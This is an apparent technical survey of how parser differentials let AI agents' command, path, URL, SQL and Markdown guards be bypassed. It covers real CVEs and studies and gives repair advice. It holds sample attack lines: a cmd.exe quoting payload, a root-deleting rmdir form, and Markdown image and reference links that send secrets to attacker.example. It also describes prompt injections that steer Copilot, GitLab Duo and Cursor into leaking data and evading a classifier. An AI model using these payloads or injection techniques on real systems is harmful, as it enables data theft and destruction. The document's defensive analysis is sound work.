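A change to the command after the guard checks it matters for security if the policy would have denied the version that runs. A content attacker might try to cause such a change through a file name or commit message that the model copies, but the study does not test whether that works.

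An earlier case shows that attackers can exploit a fault at one hop. RyotaK's *BatBadBut* (2024) reported that many programming languages could run an attacker's command on Windows when a program passed untrusted text to a batch file. Windows programs start other programs through the `CreateProcess` function. Windows cannot run a batch file directly, so `CreateProcess` starts `cmd.exe` to run it, even if the developer never asked for a shell. Microsoft's *MS14-019* (2014) had already described this behaviour.

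The language's own library and `cmd.exe` use different rules for quotation marks. RyotaK's example passes the argument `"&calc.exe` to a batch file from Node. The library puts the argument in quotation marks and a backslash before the one inside it:

`"\"&calc.exe"`

This is one piece of text under the library's rules. But `cmd.exe` doesn't use the backslash as an escape, so it reads the second quotation mark as the end of the quoted text. The `&` then starts a new command, which opens the calculator. Escaping the quotation mark the way `cmd.exe` expects is still not enough, because `cmd.exe` substitutes variables before it parses anything else.

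When RyotaK published, patches were available for Haskell, Node.js, PHP and Rust. The maintainers of Erlang, Go, Python and Ruby updated their documentation instead, and Java's maintainers declined to change anything. RyotaK chose the name to mean bad, but not the worst. The flaw affects only programs that run batch files with text an attacker can influence, and NVD's *CVE-2024-3566* (2024) also limits it to specific conditions.

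Coding agents meet those conditions more often than most software. They start many programs, with arguments that may come from documents, and common JavaScript tools such as `npm`, `npx` and `yarn` start through batch files on Windows. Yang and colleagues found that some of their test values changed when passed to these tools. A developer who does not want to run a batch file can give the program's full name, such as `test.exe`, because Windows may run `test.bat` if given only `test`. If the batch file is necessary, the developer needs a patched version of the runtime or has to apply the special escaping that RyotaK describes.

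Accidents can also do serious damage. In June 2026, a user of Cursor, a code editor with a built-in agent, asked the agent to move a folder to another drive. According to *Agent's mis-quoted rmdir command recursively deleted my entire C:\ drive*, the agent moved the folder and then tried to delete the empty original with a command of this form:

`cmd /c "rmdir /s /q \"<folder>\""`

It deleted about 200 GB from the drive. A month later, Aleksey_Nm (2026), in *[Windows] Agent Shell*, reported a command of the same form that removed some 210,000 files in about 40 seconds. The temporary folder still existed afterwards, so the agent concluded that the cleanup had failed. Cursor acknowledged in both discussions that this quoting can cause the command to delete files in the wrong place.

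Neither PowerShell nor `cmd.exe` treats `\"` as an escaped quotation mark, so the quoted text probably ended there and left a lone backslash, which means the root of the current drive, as the folder to delete. The error messages in both cases are consistent with this, since they listed paths from the drive's root. By Yang and colleagues' definition, these were probably generation errors, since the model wrote quoting that was wrong for the shells it named. But the consequence for a guard is similar, because anyone asked to approve either command would have seen the right folder's name in it.

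The agent can avoid this by deleting the folder with PowerShell's own command instead of passing text to a second shell. iceweasel-oai (2026), in *add specific tool guidance for Windows destructive commands*, added that advice to Codex's tool descriptions, along with an instruction to check the full path before any recursive deletion. This should help, but only if the model follows it. A harness can enforce the rule by refusing recursive deletions whose resolved target lies outside the workspace. A command that arrives unchanged can still get past a guard that parses it wrongly. MITRE's *CVE-2026-19591* (2026) reports that this happened with one PowerShell symbol in Codex before command-line version 0.131.0.

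### Why adding quotation marks often fails

The obvious response to a lost quotation mark is to add another. In *QuoteBench*, Li, Zhang and colleagues (2026) studied quoting in commands that pass through one extra shell. They gave models 56 tasks, each to be solved with one Bash command, and checked the resulting files and data for an exact match. They then reran the same commands inside `bash -c "..."` without escaping anything. Commands sent to a remote computer often pass through a wrapper like this.

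The extra parser reduced the success rate of all eight model configurations by 55.4 to 73.2 percentage points. The commands had not changed, so the parser must have caused the drop. Even on the 14 tasks with harmless, ordinary text, the success rate fell by 28.6 to 57.1 points, because models use double quotation marks and dollar signs in routine commands. Exit codes missed many of the failures, since between 23.4% and 47.0% of the failing commands returned the code for success.

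Some models did much better when Li and colleagues told them about the wrapper before they wrote their commands. GPT-5.6 Sol completed 94.6% of the tasks when its commands ran directly and 30.4% when the same commands went through the wrapper. When it was told about the wrapper first, it completed 91.1%. Telling the model raised the completion rate by 30.4 to 60.7 percentage points in six of the eight configurations, but didn't improve the two weakest.

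The adapted commands worked only with the wrapper, so GPT-5.6 Sol's success rate fell to 55.4% when the researchers ran its commands directly. Adding quotation marks to suit one path can therefore break a command on another, and the model often has no information about which path the harness will use.

Yang and colleagues got worse results when they told models about the path commands take to the shell. On one launch, a description cut the number of tasks Qwen2.5-Coder-32B passed from 50 to 36, partly because the model began joining commands with `&&`, which PowerShell 5.1 rejects. Showing the models both the command they sent and the one that arrived made no significant difference. These results are probably compatible with those from QuoteBench, because Yang and colleagues tested older open models on more complicated Windows paths, and the weaker models in QuoteBench did not benefit from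 a description either.

Correct escaping works if the right program does it. When Li and colleagues escaped each command at the point where the wrapper inserted it, all 448 results matched direct execution. Putting the command in a temporary script worked equally well. In a similar test with JSON, inserting commands into a JSON string without escaping them caused a loss of 51.8 to 66.1 points, while using a proper JSON writer caused no loss. The next parser is known at the point of insertion, so the component that inserts the text can apply that parser's rules. If a model adds quotation marks several steps earlier, they have to suit every parser along the way, and an extra layer that suits one parser may reach the next as ordinary characters.

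### Delivering the command or refusing it

Yang and colleagues propose a repair called INTACT, which moves the command to a channel that the faulty hop doesn't parse. The channel may be a file, a list of separate arguments, standard input (the stream from which a program can read text) or an encoded argument. If no suitable channel exists, INTACT rejects the call and reports to the agent what did not run and why.

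The choice depends on how the harness starts the shell. The last column gives the number of changed calls in the researchers' tests before and after the repair.

| Launch | Repair | Changed calls |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Code's Bash | Put the command in a file and have the same shell read it | 143 → 0 |
| PowerShell, command passed as one argument | Write each program argument by the receiving program's rules | 1,094 → 0 |
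| PowerShell, command appended after `-Command` | Write the arguments by those rules, then encode the whole command | 3,919 → 0 |
| `cmd.exe` | Refuse commands with more than one line | 41 → 0 |
| Typing into an interactive Bash | Switch off history expansion and completion first | 64 → 0 |

With Claude Code, the shell that would have run the command reads it from a file, so the working directory, environment settings and exit code stay the same. PowerShell's encoded form writes the command in Base64, which uses only letters, digits and a few symbols, so the wrapper has no quotation marks to remove.

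PowerShell 5.1 offers no channel around the Windows command line when it starts another program, so there INTACT does use escaping. It writes an argument *s* according to these rules:

```
s is empty:              ""
s contains white space:  "esc(s)β(s)"
otherwise:               esc(s)
```

Here, esc puts a backslash before each double quotation mark and doubles any backslashes directly in front of it. β repeats the backslashes at the end of *s*. For example, `C:\my files\` becomes `"C:\my files\\"`. Without the extra backslash, the receiving program would read `\"` as a quotation mark inside the argument and run the argument into the next one. The principle is the same as in QuoteBench, with the escaping done for one known parser. Requoting every argument regardless of the hop repaired only 3 of 30 deliberately introduced faults.

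To test the repair, Yang and colleagues built pairs of tasks that differed in one piece of text, so that only one version triggered a change. In 173 pairs, the harmless version had succeeded, the risky one had failed, and a hop had changed a call. When they replayed the recorded actions of these failed runs with the responsible hops repaired, 137 (79.2%) succeeded. As a control, they did the same with 187 failed pairs in which no call had changed, and none succeeded. The 79.2% applies to this benchmark and doesn't estimate the share of production failures that INTACT would prevent.

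In 22 of the 36 pairs that still failed, the agent had made its mistake in an action that no hop changed. In another 12, it had given up after a misleading error, so there was no correct later action to replay. The remaining two used a construct the repair cannot handle.

Some paths needed two repairs, because the wrapper and the process interface could each damage a command that the harness appended after `-Command`. Repairing both recovered 69 pairs. Repairing only the wrapper recovered 31 of these, and repairing only the process interface recovered none, because the wrapper had already consumed the quotation marks. A developer who fixes one hop has to test the path again, because the fix may uncover a fault at the next.

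During the last three weeks of the production study, INTACT sent 3,577 Bash calls through files. Of these, 227 would otherwise have changed, and none did. The median delay was 4 milliseconds per call. The researchers measured their own tool, and no independent trial appears to exist yet. The method is simple enough that a developer could pass commands through a file without installing INTACT.

Moving a command into a file can hide it from the guard. If the harness checks its permission rules after the rewrite, it checks only an instruction to read a file, and a rule that forbids a particular program no longer matches because the program's name is in the file. Yang and colleagues therefore require the harness to apply the permission rules to the original command, as their Claude Code version does.

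## Checking commands, file paths, web addresses and database queries

A guard that checks the original command must still determine what the command will do. Many guards use a simple rule, such as looking up the first word in a list, but the shell and the program it starts interpret the command using a much larger grammar. Checks on file paths, web addresses and database queries often have the same weakness, as did the filter that searched raw JSON for "credentials".

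| Text | What a simple check reads | What the program reads |
|---|---|---|
| Command | The first word and a few forbidden options | Shell syntax, then the called program's own options |
| File path | The characters at the start | A chain of folders, any of which may be a link |
| Web address | The characters at the start of the host name | A host name whose ending determines who owns it |
| Database query | How the text begins | One or more complete statements |

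These attacks often require less access than the attacks on JSON arguments, most of which assumed a compromised gateway. The model writes the command or path, and the text can be valid, so a content attacker can try to make the model write it through prompt injection. Most of Anthropic's advisories on these flaws state that a reliable attack requires untrusted content in the model's context. The people who found the flaws showed that the checks fail, but they did not measure how often a model would write the necessary text.

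### Commands

A coding agent would be tiresome to use if a person had to approve every directory listing, so Claude Code runs some commands without asking. Beber's *InversePrompt* reproduces the list of permitted commands from an early version. It contains about 70 regular expressions, most of which permit a command that only reads data. For instance, the pattern for `sort` allowed the command unless it included the option that writes the result to a file.

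Beber, a researcher at the security company Cymulate, found a flaw in how Claude Code handled `echo`, a command that prints its arguments (CVE-2025-54795). A quotation mark in the right place ended the text to be printed, and the shell ran what followed as a separate command. Claude Code treated the whole line as one harmless `echo`, so it didn't ask the user for approval. OSV's *GHSA-x56v-x2h6-7j34* (2025) attributes this to an error in command parsing and lists 1.0.20 as the fixed version. Anthropic later forced everyone on versions before 1.0.24 to update.

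The patterns had other gaps. RyotaK (2026), in *Pwning Claude Code in 8 Different Ways*, describes eight ways to run a command of the attacker's choice without approval, which share the number CVE-2025-66032. In about half of them, Claude Code identified the right program but overlooked something it could do:

- `man`, which displays manual pages, can start another program to show them. The check blocked the short name of one such option but not its long name.
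- `sort` has an option that names a program for compressing its temporary files.
- `history`, which lists earlier commands, can also write to a file.
- `sed`, which edits text, has a command of its own that runs shell commands.

These are mainly faults in the policy, because better parsing would not have shown that compressing a temporary file was dangerous. The remaining four are parser differentials. For example, Git accepts shortened forms of its long option names, but the check matched only the full name of the forbidden option, so an abbreviation passed the check and Git expanded it.

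The check on `xargs`, which runs another command on a list of inputs, allowed a value after any option, but some options take none. After one of these, the check skipped the next word as if it were a value and approved the harmless command name that followed. `xargs` instead ran the skipped word as the command and passed the harmless name to it as an argument.

For the search tool ripgrep, the check accepted any run of characters without a space as a single search term. But the shell substitutes variables before it runs ripgrep, and a variable's value can contain a space. A single term could therefore reach ripgrep as several arguments, including an option that starts another program. The last flaw involved Bash syntax that expands a variable's value a second time, which can run a command. Claude Code did not recognise this syntax and treated the command as another `echo`.

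GitLab's *CVE-2025-66032* (2025), which carries Anthropic's advisory, rates the flaws 8.8 out of 10. Version 1.0.93 fixes them. According to RyotaK, Anthropic replaced its lists of forbidden patterns with lists of what it permits.

GitHub's command-line agent, Copilot CLI, had a similar problem with Bash variables a few months later. It required approval for commands that did more than read data, but it classed some commands as read-only even though an expansion in their arguments could run code. According to NVD's *CVE-2026-29783 Detail*, an attacker could influence the command through repository files or replies from MCP servers. Version 0.0.423 fixes the flaw.

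In Cursor, a command the user approved could start a program chosen by an attacker. Lisichkin (2026) found in *The Agent Security Paradox* that Cursor ran certain shell built-ins, which are commands the shell carries out itself, without approval even if the user's allowlist was empty. An attacker could use built-ins that set environment variables to change which program Git starts to display its output, and that program would run when the user approved `git branch`. Other built-ins could write a file or run a command directly, without any approval.

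The effect of `git branch` depended on a setting from an earlier command, so reading its unchanged text more carefully would not have helped. This is why Yang and colleagues include the environment when they specify a shell action. A guard has to take the environment into account too, or the harness has to start each command with a known environment.

Lisichkin reported the flaw in August 2025, and the fix came out in January 2026. NVD's *CVE-2026-22708 Detail* lists Cursor 2.3 as the fixed version. The editor now asks for approval whenever its parser cannot classify a command, and Cursor's security guidelines advise against relying on the allowlist, which they describe as "best-effort".

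A better command check first splits the text the way the intended shell does and refuses any construct the check does not support, including expansions. It then compares the command with descriptions of the permitted programs, which list each program's permitted options and whether each option takes a value. Anything outside these descriptions goes to the user for approval. Writing the descriptions for a few dozen programs is a lot of work, and they have to match the versions installed on the user's computer.

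### File paths

Suppose an agent may use only the folder `/work/data`:

```
permitted folder: /work/data
requested file:   /work/data-private/keys.txt
```

If the permitted folder is `data`, a check that compares only the first characters of a path will also allow a request for `data-private`. The file system separates names at each slash, so it treats `data-private` as a different folder beside `data`.

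An early version of Claude Code used this kind of comparison to keep the agent inside its working folder (CVE-2025-54794). The code first resolved steps such as `..`, which means the folder above, so an attacker could not use them to leave the folder. But it then compared the two resolved paths as plain text. According to GCVE (2025), an attack required a folder whose name began with the working folder's name, or the ability to create one. That limits the damage, but it is not unusual for a project folder to have a backup or private copy beside it. Version 0.2.111 fixes the flaw.

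Beber's *EscapeRoute* describes the same comparison in Anthropic's reference MCP server for files, where the flaw is listed as CVE-2025-53110. The operator lists the permitted folders when starting the server, which was supposed to refuse every path outside them.

The same server also mishandled symbolic links (CVE-2025-53109). A symbolic link is a folder entry that points to another location, so a path inside a permitted folder can lead to a file anywhere on the disk. The server's developers had anticipated this, and their code looked up a link's real target and raised an error if it lay outside the permitted folders.

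The server mishandled the error. The lookup also fails when a file does not exist yet, which is normal when an agent is creating one, so the developers had written an error handler that checked the folder the new file would go into. But the handler also caught the error raised for a forbidden target. It then checked the folder that contained the link, found it permitted, and returned the original path as safe. The server opened that path, and the operating system followed the link to the forbidden file.

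Beber used the flaw to write a file that macOS runs when the user logs in, which let him run code outside the agent. To place the link, the attacker first needs write access to a suitable folder or a tool that can create links. GitLab's *CVE-2025-53110* (2025) and *CVE-2025-53109* (2025) both tell users to upgrade to version 2025.7.1, which Anthropic released on July 1, 2025, three months after Beber's report.

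A sound check resolves both paths to their real locations, including any links. Write *d* for the permitted folder's real path and *r* for the requested one. The check allows the request only if

*r* = *d*, or *r* begins with *d* followed by a slash.

When the allowed prefix ends in a slash (`/work/data/`), `/work/data/report.txt` passes and `/work/data-private/keys.txt` does not. If a file does not exist yet, the check can resolve its parent folder and then add the file's name. The check should also distinguish a missing file from a forbidden one, and refuse the request after any other error.

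A link can still change after the check but before the program opens the file. The operating system can prevent this by resolving the path and enforcing the limit in one step. Linux, for example, lets a program require, when it opens a file, that the path stay inside a given folder.

A link can also bypass a rule that forbids a file, because it gives the file a second path that a check on the text won't match. goard, an unofficial viewer for GitHub's pages, lists two Claude Code advisories about such bypasses, from October 2025 and February 2026. The remedy is again to apply the rule to the file's real location.

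### Web addresses

Claude Code's WebFetch tool retrieves web pages. It can do this without asking if the page is on a trusted site, such as the documentation for a programming language. OSV's *GHSA-vhw5-3g5m-8ggf* (2026) records that the tool tested whether the requested domain began with a trusted one. Domain names work in the other direction, because the owner of a domain controls every name that ends with it:

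```
trusted:   docs.example.org
requested: docs.example.org.attacker.example
```

The requested domain name begins with the trusted one but belongs to whoever owns `attacker.example`, so a prefix check allows the request and it goes to the attacker's server. An agent can leak data this way even if it only retrieves a page, because it may put private text into the address. Claude Code 1.0.111 fixes the flaw, which OSV rates 7.1 out of 10.

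The 2009 certificate attack used a similar name but relied on a null character, whereas this address contains nothing unusual.

The guard can parse the address with the same library as the program that will fetch the page, then compare the full host name with the list. To allow subdomains, it can also accept host names that end in a dot followed by a trusted domain. Without the dot, `notexample.org` would pass as `example.org`. Searching the full address for a trusted name is no better than a prefix check, because the name can appear in the path or in the user name before an `@`. The fetching program also has to repeat the check for every redirect, since a trusted page may redirect to a host that isn't on the list.

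These checks identify the host but not the person who published the page. In June 2026, according to goard's list, Anthropic published an advisory about data leaking through a Hugging Face domain that WebFetch had approved in advance. Hugging Face hosts models and files from many people, so a list of trusted hosts can be too coarse for such a site. Asking before each fetch would avoid the problem, but an agent that reads dozens of pages for one task would interrupt its user for each one.

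### Database queries

Anthropic's reference MCP server for PostgreSQL, a widely used database, was supposed to let an agent read data but not change it. It placed each query inside a read-only transaction. A transaction is a group of statements that the database handles together, and PostgreSQL refuses any change inside a read-only one. The server took three steps:

1. It opened a read-only transaction.
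2. It sent the agent's query.
3. It closed the transaction and cancelled any effects.

Datadog Security Labs' *MCP vulnerability case study* (2025) shows how this went wrong. The server treated the agent's text as one query, but the software that passed it to PostgreSQL accepted several statements in a row. The text could therefore include one statement that closed the transaction and another that deleted every table. When the server then tried to cancel the transaction, it had already ended. PostgreSQL would have refused the deletion if it had been the only statement in the text.

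Datadog's fix sends the text as a prepared statement, a request that PostgreSQL accepts only if it contains a single statement. The database's own parser determines where the statement ends, so the server does not have to search for semicolons, which can also appear inside ordinary text.

The patch reached users slowly. A researcher reported the flaw in November 2024, eight days after the server's first release. Datadog found it independently and sent Anthropic a patch in April 2025. A version maintained by Zed Industries, which makes a code editor, adopted the patch that month. Anthropic fixed its source code on May 29 and archived the project the same day, but the published package stayed unpatched and still had about 21,000 downloads a week in August 2025. An operator therefore has to check the installed package, because a fix in the source code may never have reached it.

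Other database servers used weaker checks. CIRCL, Luxembourg's computer incident response centre, described one that tested whether a query began with `SELECT`, the keyword for reading data. Its database software accepted several statements in one query, so a statement that changed data could follow the `SELECT`. Even a single `SELECT` can change data if it calls a function that does so.

A check can also miss part of a query. PointGuard AI's *Three Database MCP Servers Break in Three Different Ways (CVE-2025-66335)* summarises research by the internet company Akamai on the server for Apache Doris, another database. The server's validator examined only the first part of the query and missed text that arrived through a separate field for the database's name. The flaw affects versions below 0.6.1. The validator should have examined the whole query after the server had assembled it.

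Amazon's PostgreSQL server used a list of forbidden SQL, and two flaws in it became public within a week in September 2026. AWS's *CVE-2026-85787* (2026) describes an incomplete list that could let an attacker change data in read-only mode. AWS's *CVE-2026-87911* (2026) describes a more serious flaw. The read-only check failed to block a PostgreSQL statement that exports data by passing it to another program, so an attacker could run commands on the database's computer. Version 1.1.7 fixes both flaws.

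The second flaw affected only databases that the operator ran directly, and only if the server logged in with a role (a database account with its own permissions) that was allowed to start programs. With a more limited role, PostgreSQL would have rejected the statement even though the check had missed it.

### Why longer blocklists keep failing

Write *D* for the set of all dangerous inputs, *B* for those that a blocklist forbids and *A* for those that an allowlist permits. The two kinds of list are safe under different conditions:

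- Blocklist: every member of *D* is in *B*.
- Allowlist: no member of *A* is in *D*.

To meet the first condition, a blocklist's author has to know every dangerous input to every permitted program. An allowlist's author only has to understand the inputs on the list. A blocklist lets through an option its author has never heard of, while an allowlist leaves the decision to the user. A blocklist can also become less safe without anyone editing it, because a new version of a program may add options.

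Claude Code's pattern for `man` shows that forbidding one more item may achieve little. The early version that Beber reproduced forbade two spellings of the option for choosing a display program. The version RyotaK tested also forbade several more special characters and the short name of a related option, so he bypassed it with that option's long name. Forbidding the long name too would have closed this gap, but not the ones in `sort`, `sed` or Git.

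Regular expressions make commands harder to check because shell syntax can nest, with a command inside quotation marks inside another command. A regular expression in the strict sense cannot match nesting of unlimited depth. A pattern can reject the characters that begin nested constructs, but developers use many of these characters in ordinary work, so a strict pattern also blocks harmless commands. Each exception added for convenience has to be safe in every position where it can occur.

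An allowlist can still fail if the software misparses a command or the list permits unsafe ones. OSV's *GHSA-qgqw-h4xq-7w8w* (2026) reports that Claude Code misparsed the file-search command `find` and lists every version before 2.0.72 as affected, including those released after Anthropic's change of approach. OSV's *GHSA-7mv8-j34q-vp7q* (2025) and *GHSA-mhg7-666j-cqg4* (2026) concern further ways to write files with `sed`. OSV's *GHSA-x5gv-jw7f-j6xj* (2025) reports that the allowlist itself permitted commands that could read a file and send its contents over the network.

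Goard lists 30 advisories for Claude Code between June 2025 and June 2026, and at least six concern a command that the approval check mishandled. This suggests that fixing one command at a time leaves others that the check still mishandles. The count doesn't mean that Claude Code is worse than its competitors, since a popular product with a public reporting programme attracts more researchers.

### Using the receiver's own parser

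The guard can instead use the same parser as the program that will act on the output. This works well for web addresses, where the guard and the fetching program can share a library. It can also work for SQL, since developers can get PostgreSQL's parser as a separate library and examine the parsed statement it returns. They have to keep the library at the same version as the database, and they still need a policy for the functions a query may call.

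Commands are much harder to check, because the shell has one parser and every program it starts has another. Few programs can report how they would interpret their options without running. The result may also depend on variables that exist only when the command runs. A guard can refuse any command it cannot resolve in advance, but developers routinely use variables and loops, so it would often interrupt them. People who see many prompts may start approving them without reading, which removes much of the protection.

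### Accepting separate arguments

A tool can avoid much of the parsing by never accepting a whole command or query. For shell commands, it can take the program's name and a list of arguments and start the program without a shell, so variables and semicolons have no special meaning. This would have stopped Beber's `echo` attack and RyotaK's attacks with shell variables, but it would not have helped with `man`, `sort`, Git, `sed` or `xargs`, whose own options caused the problem.

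A narrower tool can prevent those as well. For file searches, the harness can offer a tool with fields for the text and the folder, and add the options itself. For databases, Microsoft (2026) describes its SQL MCP Server, which offers the agent only the tables, views and stored procedures the operator has listed, and only the operations the current role permits. The server writes the SQL from the fields the agent fills in.

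Limiting an agent to predefined tools makes it less flexible. Someone has to design each tool, and an agent that can run only a fixed set of searches can't answer a question nobody expected. Without a shell, it also can't use the short combinations of programs that make command lines useful. Datadog notes that ordinary applications would never run arbitrary SQL from a user, but that agents often need more open-ended tools. A few fixed operations are probably enough for an airline's booking agent, but usually not for a coding agent.

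### Enforcing the limit where the action happens

The operating system or the database can enforce the limit without interpreting the text first. A sandbox restricts what a running program can do, for example which folders it can write to and which network addresses it can reach. If the guard misreads an option and `sort` starts an unexpected program, that program runs under the same restrictions.

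AWS gives similar advice for databases and calls a role with minimal permissions the strongest control. An agent that only reads needs only permission to connect and to read the relevant tables, and the operator should never give it an administrator's account. AWS sensibly recommends keeping the blocklist as a second layer. Forkast, a trade news site, warns that filters and parsers in front of a database don't replace the database's own limits.

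A limited role doesn't prevent every kind of harm. Datadog found that the PostgreSQL server reused connections, so one query could change a connection's settings for the next user. An attacker with no permission to change data could set a time limit of one millisecond, after which almost every query on that connection failed. Datadog's patch therefore also closes the connection after each call, which is slightly slower but leaves no settings behind.

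Roles also need upkeep. When a developer adds a table, the agent may be unable to read it until someone extends the permissions. An agent that sometimes has to write needs a second role, and the harness has to switch to it when needed. Sandboxes cause similar problems for coding agents, which often install packages, contact test servers or use files outside the project. Each of these actions fails until the user loosens the limits, and a user in a hurry may loosen them too much.

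Lisichkin would go further and abandon allowlists, letting agents run any command in an isolated environment. That suits work on a disposable copy of a project with no valuable passwords or network access. But a sandbox doesn't stop an agent from deleting a file inside the project that the user wanted to keep. If the agent is logged in to a live service, it can also do damage through a connection the sandbox permits. Those actions still need to be checked by a person or by a guard that can interpret the request.

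Sandboxes have flaws too. The aggregator vuln.today lists an escape from Claude Code's sandbox that allowed writes outside the workspace, fixed in version 2.1.64. Another escape, fixed in version 2.1.163, let a malicious repository break out of the sandbox on macOS through Git worktrees, which are multiple working copies of one repository. Both escapes involved symbolic links.

For most coding agents, the best compromise is probably a sandbox with few exceptions and an allowlist in front of it. The sandbox limits the damage from a misread command, so the allowlist mainly determines when to interrupt the user. The choice is easier for database agents, because a read-only role takes little work to set up and stops most harmful queries without filtering their text.

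## Displaying model output in a browser, chat window or terminal

When the airline's agent tells a customer that it has cancelled a booking, usually no guard checks the message, because it is meant for a person to read. But a program must parse the message to display it, and parsing can have side effects. A browser may load an image from another server, and a terminal may clear the screen. A content attacker who can influence the reply may therefore cause an action without any tool call.

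### How an image carries data out

Many chat interfaces have the model write Markdown, a simple notation for formatted text. Two asterisks on each side of a word make it bold, and a label in square brackets followed by an address in round ones makes a link. The interface converts the Markdown to HTML, the language of web pages, for the browser to display. An exclamation mark in front of a link turns it into an image:

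`![Map](https://attacker.example/map.png?d=I3EHXC)`

To show the picture, the browser sends the server a request that includes the picture's address. Here the address ends in a reservation number, so whoever runs the server can read the number in its log, even if the picture does not exist. An ordinary link can send the same data, but only if the user clicks it.

The attack also needs a prompt injection and a model with access to data worth stealing. Willison (2025), a software developer who writes about AI, had seen this kind of leak in a dozen products by June 2025. The program that displays the reply can do little to prevent the injection or limit the model's access to data, but it can stop the data from being sent out.

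OWASP recommends encoding a model's output to suit the place where it will appear. For a web page, this means writing `<` as `&lt;`, so that the browser shows an HTML tag as text instead of acting on it. Encoding stops raw HTML but not the Markdown image above, which contains no tag until the interface converts it. Encoding everything after the conversion would also disable the bold text and links that the developer wants. Most interfaces therefore use a filter with a parser to allow some formatting and remove the rest.

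### EchoLeak: a filter and a renderer that read links differently

Microsoft 365 Copilot answers employees' questions using their company's emails, files and chats. In *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration*, Ravia (2025) describes how his team at Aim Labs, a security research group, used a single email to make Copilot send this data to an outside server. The attack worked once the victim asked Copilot a question that led it to retrieve the email, without the victim clicking anything.

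To make that more likely, the researchers repeated their instructions under headings about common topics, such as onboarding and leave. They addressed the text to the employee and never mentioned an AI, so Microsoft's prompt injection classifier did not flag it.

Copilot removed links to outside addresses before it displayed a reply. The filter recognised the usual way of writing a link:

`[Report](https://attacker.example/?d=SECRET)`

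But Markdown also allows a reference link, which puts the address on a line of its own:

```
[Report][ref]

[ref]: https://attacker.example/?d=SECRET
```

The renderer, which converts the Markdown for display, turned both versions into working links. The filter missed the second version and images written in the same style.

This meets the harm condition. The filter is the guard, the renderer is the executor, and the policy forbids outside addresses. The policy allowed the reply because *G*(*b*) contained no link, but *E*(*b*) contained a link that the policy would have denied.

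Making the filter recognize reference links would have helped, but Ravia lists shorter variants that also got through, and like any blocklist, a filter that matches specific forms misses those not on its list. It is more reliable to convert the Markdown to HTML with the renderer the page uses and then check every address in the result, because by then all the ways of writing an image have become the same tag. The check has to come after the last program that changes the HTML, and it is safest in the browser, because a filter on the server may parse the HTML differently than the browser does.

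Copilot had a second barrier, a Content Security Policy, which is a set of rules that a website sends to the browser. The policy can list the hosts from which a page may load images. The browser applies this list to the request itself, so the syntax the model used for the image makes no difference. The attacker's server was not on the list, so the browser refused to contact it.

But the list had nearly 30 entries, including Microsoft's SharePoint and Teams. Ravia's team found a Teams address that would fetch any address given to it as a parameter. The browser requested an "image" from Teams, as the list permitted, and Teams passed the secret on to the attacker's server. A SharePoint address did the same, but only if the user had accepted an invitation to the attacker's site.

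The rule allowed requests to entire hosts, and one of those hosts relayed requests for outsiders. No program misread anything at this step. A site's operator can limit the allowed hosts to those that only serve stored files, but a company with many services may not know which of them fetch URLs on request.

In its record of the flaw, reproduced in GCVE's *CVE-2025-32711* (2025), Microsoft rates the severity 9.3 out of 10 and marks Copilot as a hosted service. Microsoft fixed the flaw on its own servers, and Willison reports that the fix was in place by June 11, 2025. Microsoft confirms in the record that an outsider could obtain data from Copilot but describes the flaw in a single sentence, so the account of the link filter depends on Ravia's report. Microsoft filed the flaw under a general class for injection instead of CWE-436, Interpretation Conflict. Either class fits, since the attack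 began with injected instructions and succeeded because of a parser differential. Ravia reports that Microsoft found no affected customers.

### Replies that the browser renders too early

Chat interfaces usually display a reply while the model is still writing it, so a check on the complete reply can come too late. GitLab Duo, an AI assistant on a website where developers store and review code, rendered its answers line by line. In Legit Security's *Remote Prompt Injection in GitLab Duo Leads to Source Code Theft*, researchers hid instructions in a public project. When a user asked Duo about a file there, Duo fetched code from one of the user's private projects, encoded it in Base64 and put it into the address of an image. Duo could fetch the code because it had the same access as the user. The same method could have exposed confidential reports of unpatched security flaws.

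Legit Security attributes the flaw to the line-by-line rendering, which turned a raw `<img>` tag into a live image before the parser knew the structure of the whole answer. That is probably only part of the problem. Duo also passed its answers through DOMPurify, a widely used library that removes dangerous HTML but keeps images, forms and links by default, because it mainly guards against scripts. An image outside a code block would presumably have survived even if Duo had waited for the full answer before rendering it.

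Since GitLab's fix, Duo no longer renders images, forms and similar tags that point to a domain outside gitlab.com. This also prevents it from showing harmless pictures from other sites.

A later attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot clearly worked because of timing. Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026) reports that Copilot's search page protected users by wrapping HTML in a code block, which makes the browser show it as text. The page wrapped the HTML only after the reply was complete. Until then, the browser treated the HTML as part of the page, so it had already requested an image in the HTML before the wrapping was applied.

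Write *b*<sub>*k*</sub> for the first *k* characters of a reply that is *n* characters long, and *R*(*b*<sub>*k*</sub>) for what the browser makes of them. Copilot in effect checked only *R*(*b*<sub>*n*</sub>). A streamed reply is safe only if

*P*(*R*(*b*<sub>*k*</sub>)) = allow for every *k* from 1 to *n*.

The attack began with a link to Microsoft's own website with a prompt in the search field. When the victim clicked it, Copilot ran the prompt, searched the victim's mailbox and put the title of an email into an image address. The title may be enough, because some services put login codes there. The browser could not load the image directly from the attacker's server, so the address went through Bing's image search, which was on the page's list of permitted hosts and fetches a picture from any address it receives. Bing had also been on the list that Ravia published a year earlier. Microsoft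 rated the flaw, CVE-2026-42824, as critical and has fixed it.

Varonis recommends sanitizing model output when it is rendered. During streaming, a tag can arrive in two pieces, so the program has to parse all the text received so far whenever more arrives, and hold back a link or image until it is complete. A simpler interface could show plain text during streaming and add the formatting at the end. Users would see raw asterisks for a few seconds, but nothing would load during that time.

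### Diagrams written as code

A reply can also contain a second language with its own parser. Many interfaces support Mermaid, which draws diagrams from short descriptions. This one produces two boxes joined by an arrow:

```
graph TD
  User --> Computer
```

A Markdown parser treats these lines as a code block, so a filter that checks the parser's output finds no links or images. But the interface passes the block to Mermaid, and a box in a Mermaid diagram can contain HTML. JSON text inside a string argument is similar, because the first parser treats it as an ordinary string and doesn't parse its contents.

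In Embrace The Red's *Cursor IDE*, the security researcher Johann Rehberger used this against Cursor. He hid instructions in a comment in a small program and asked Cursor to explain the file. Cursor drew a diagram with an image whose address contained what the editor had stored about the user. In a second demonstration, the address contained secret access keys from a configuration file. Rehberger notes that the diagram simply appeared, so a user had no chance to see the data as the model wrote it.

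He reported the flaw on June 30, 2025, and Cursor released a fix in version 1.3 a month later. According to MITRE's *Cursor* (2025), people found further ways around that fix, and version 1.7 closes them.

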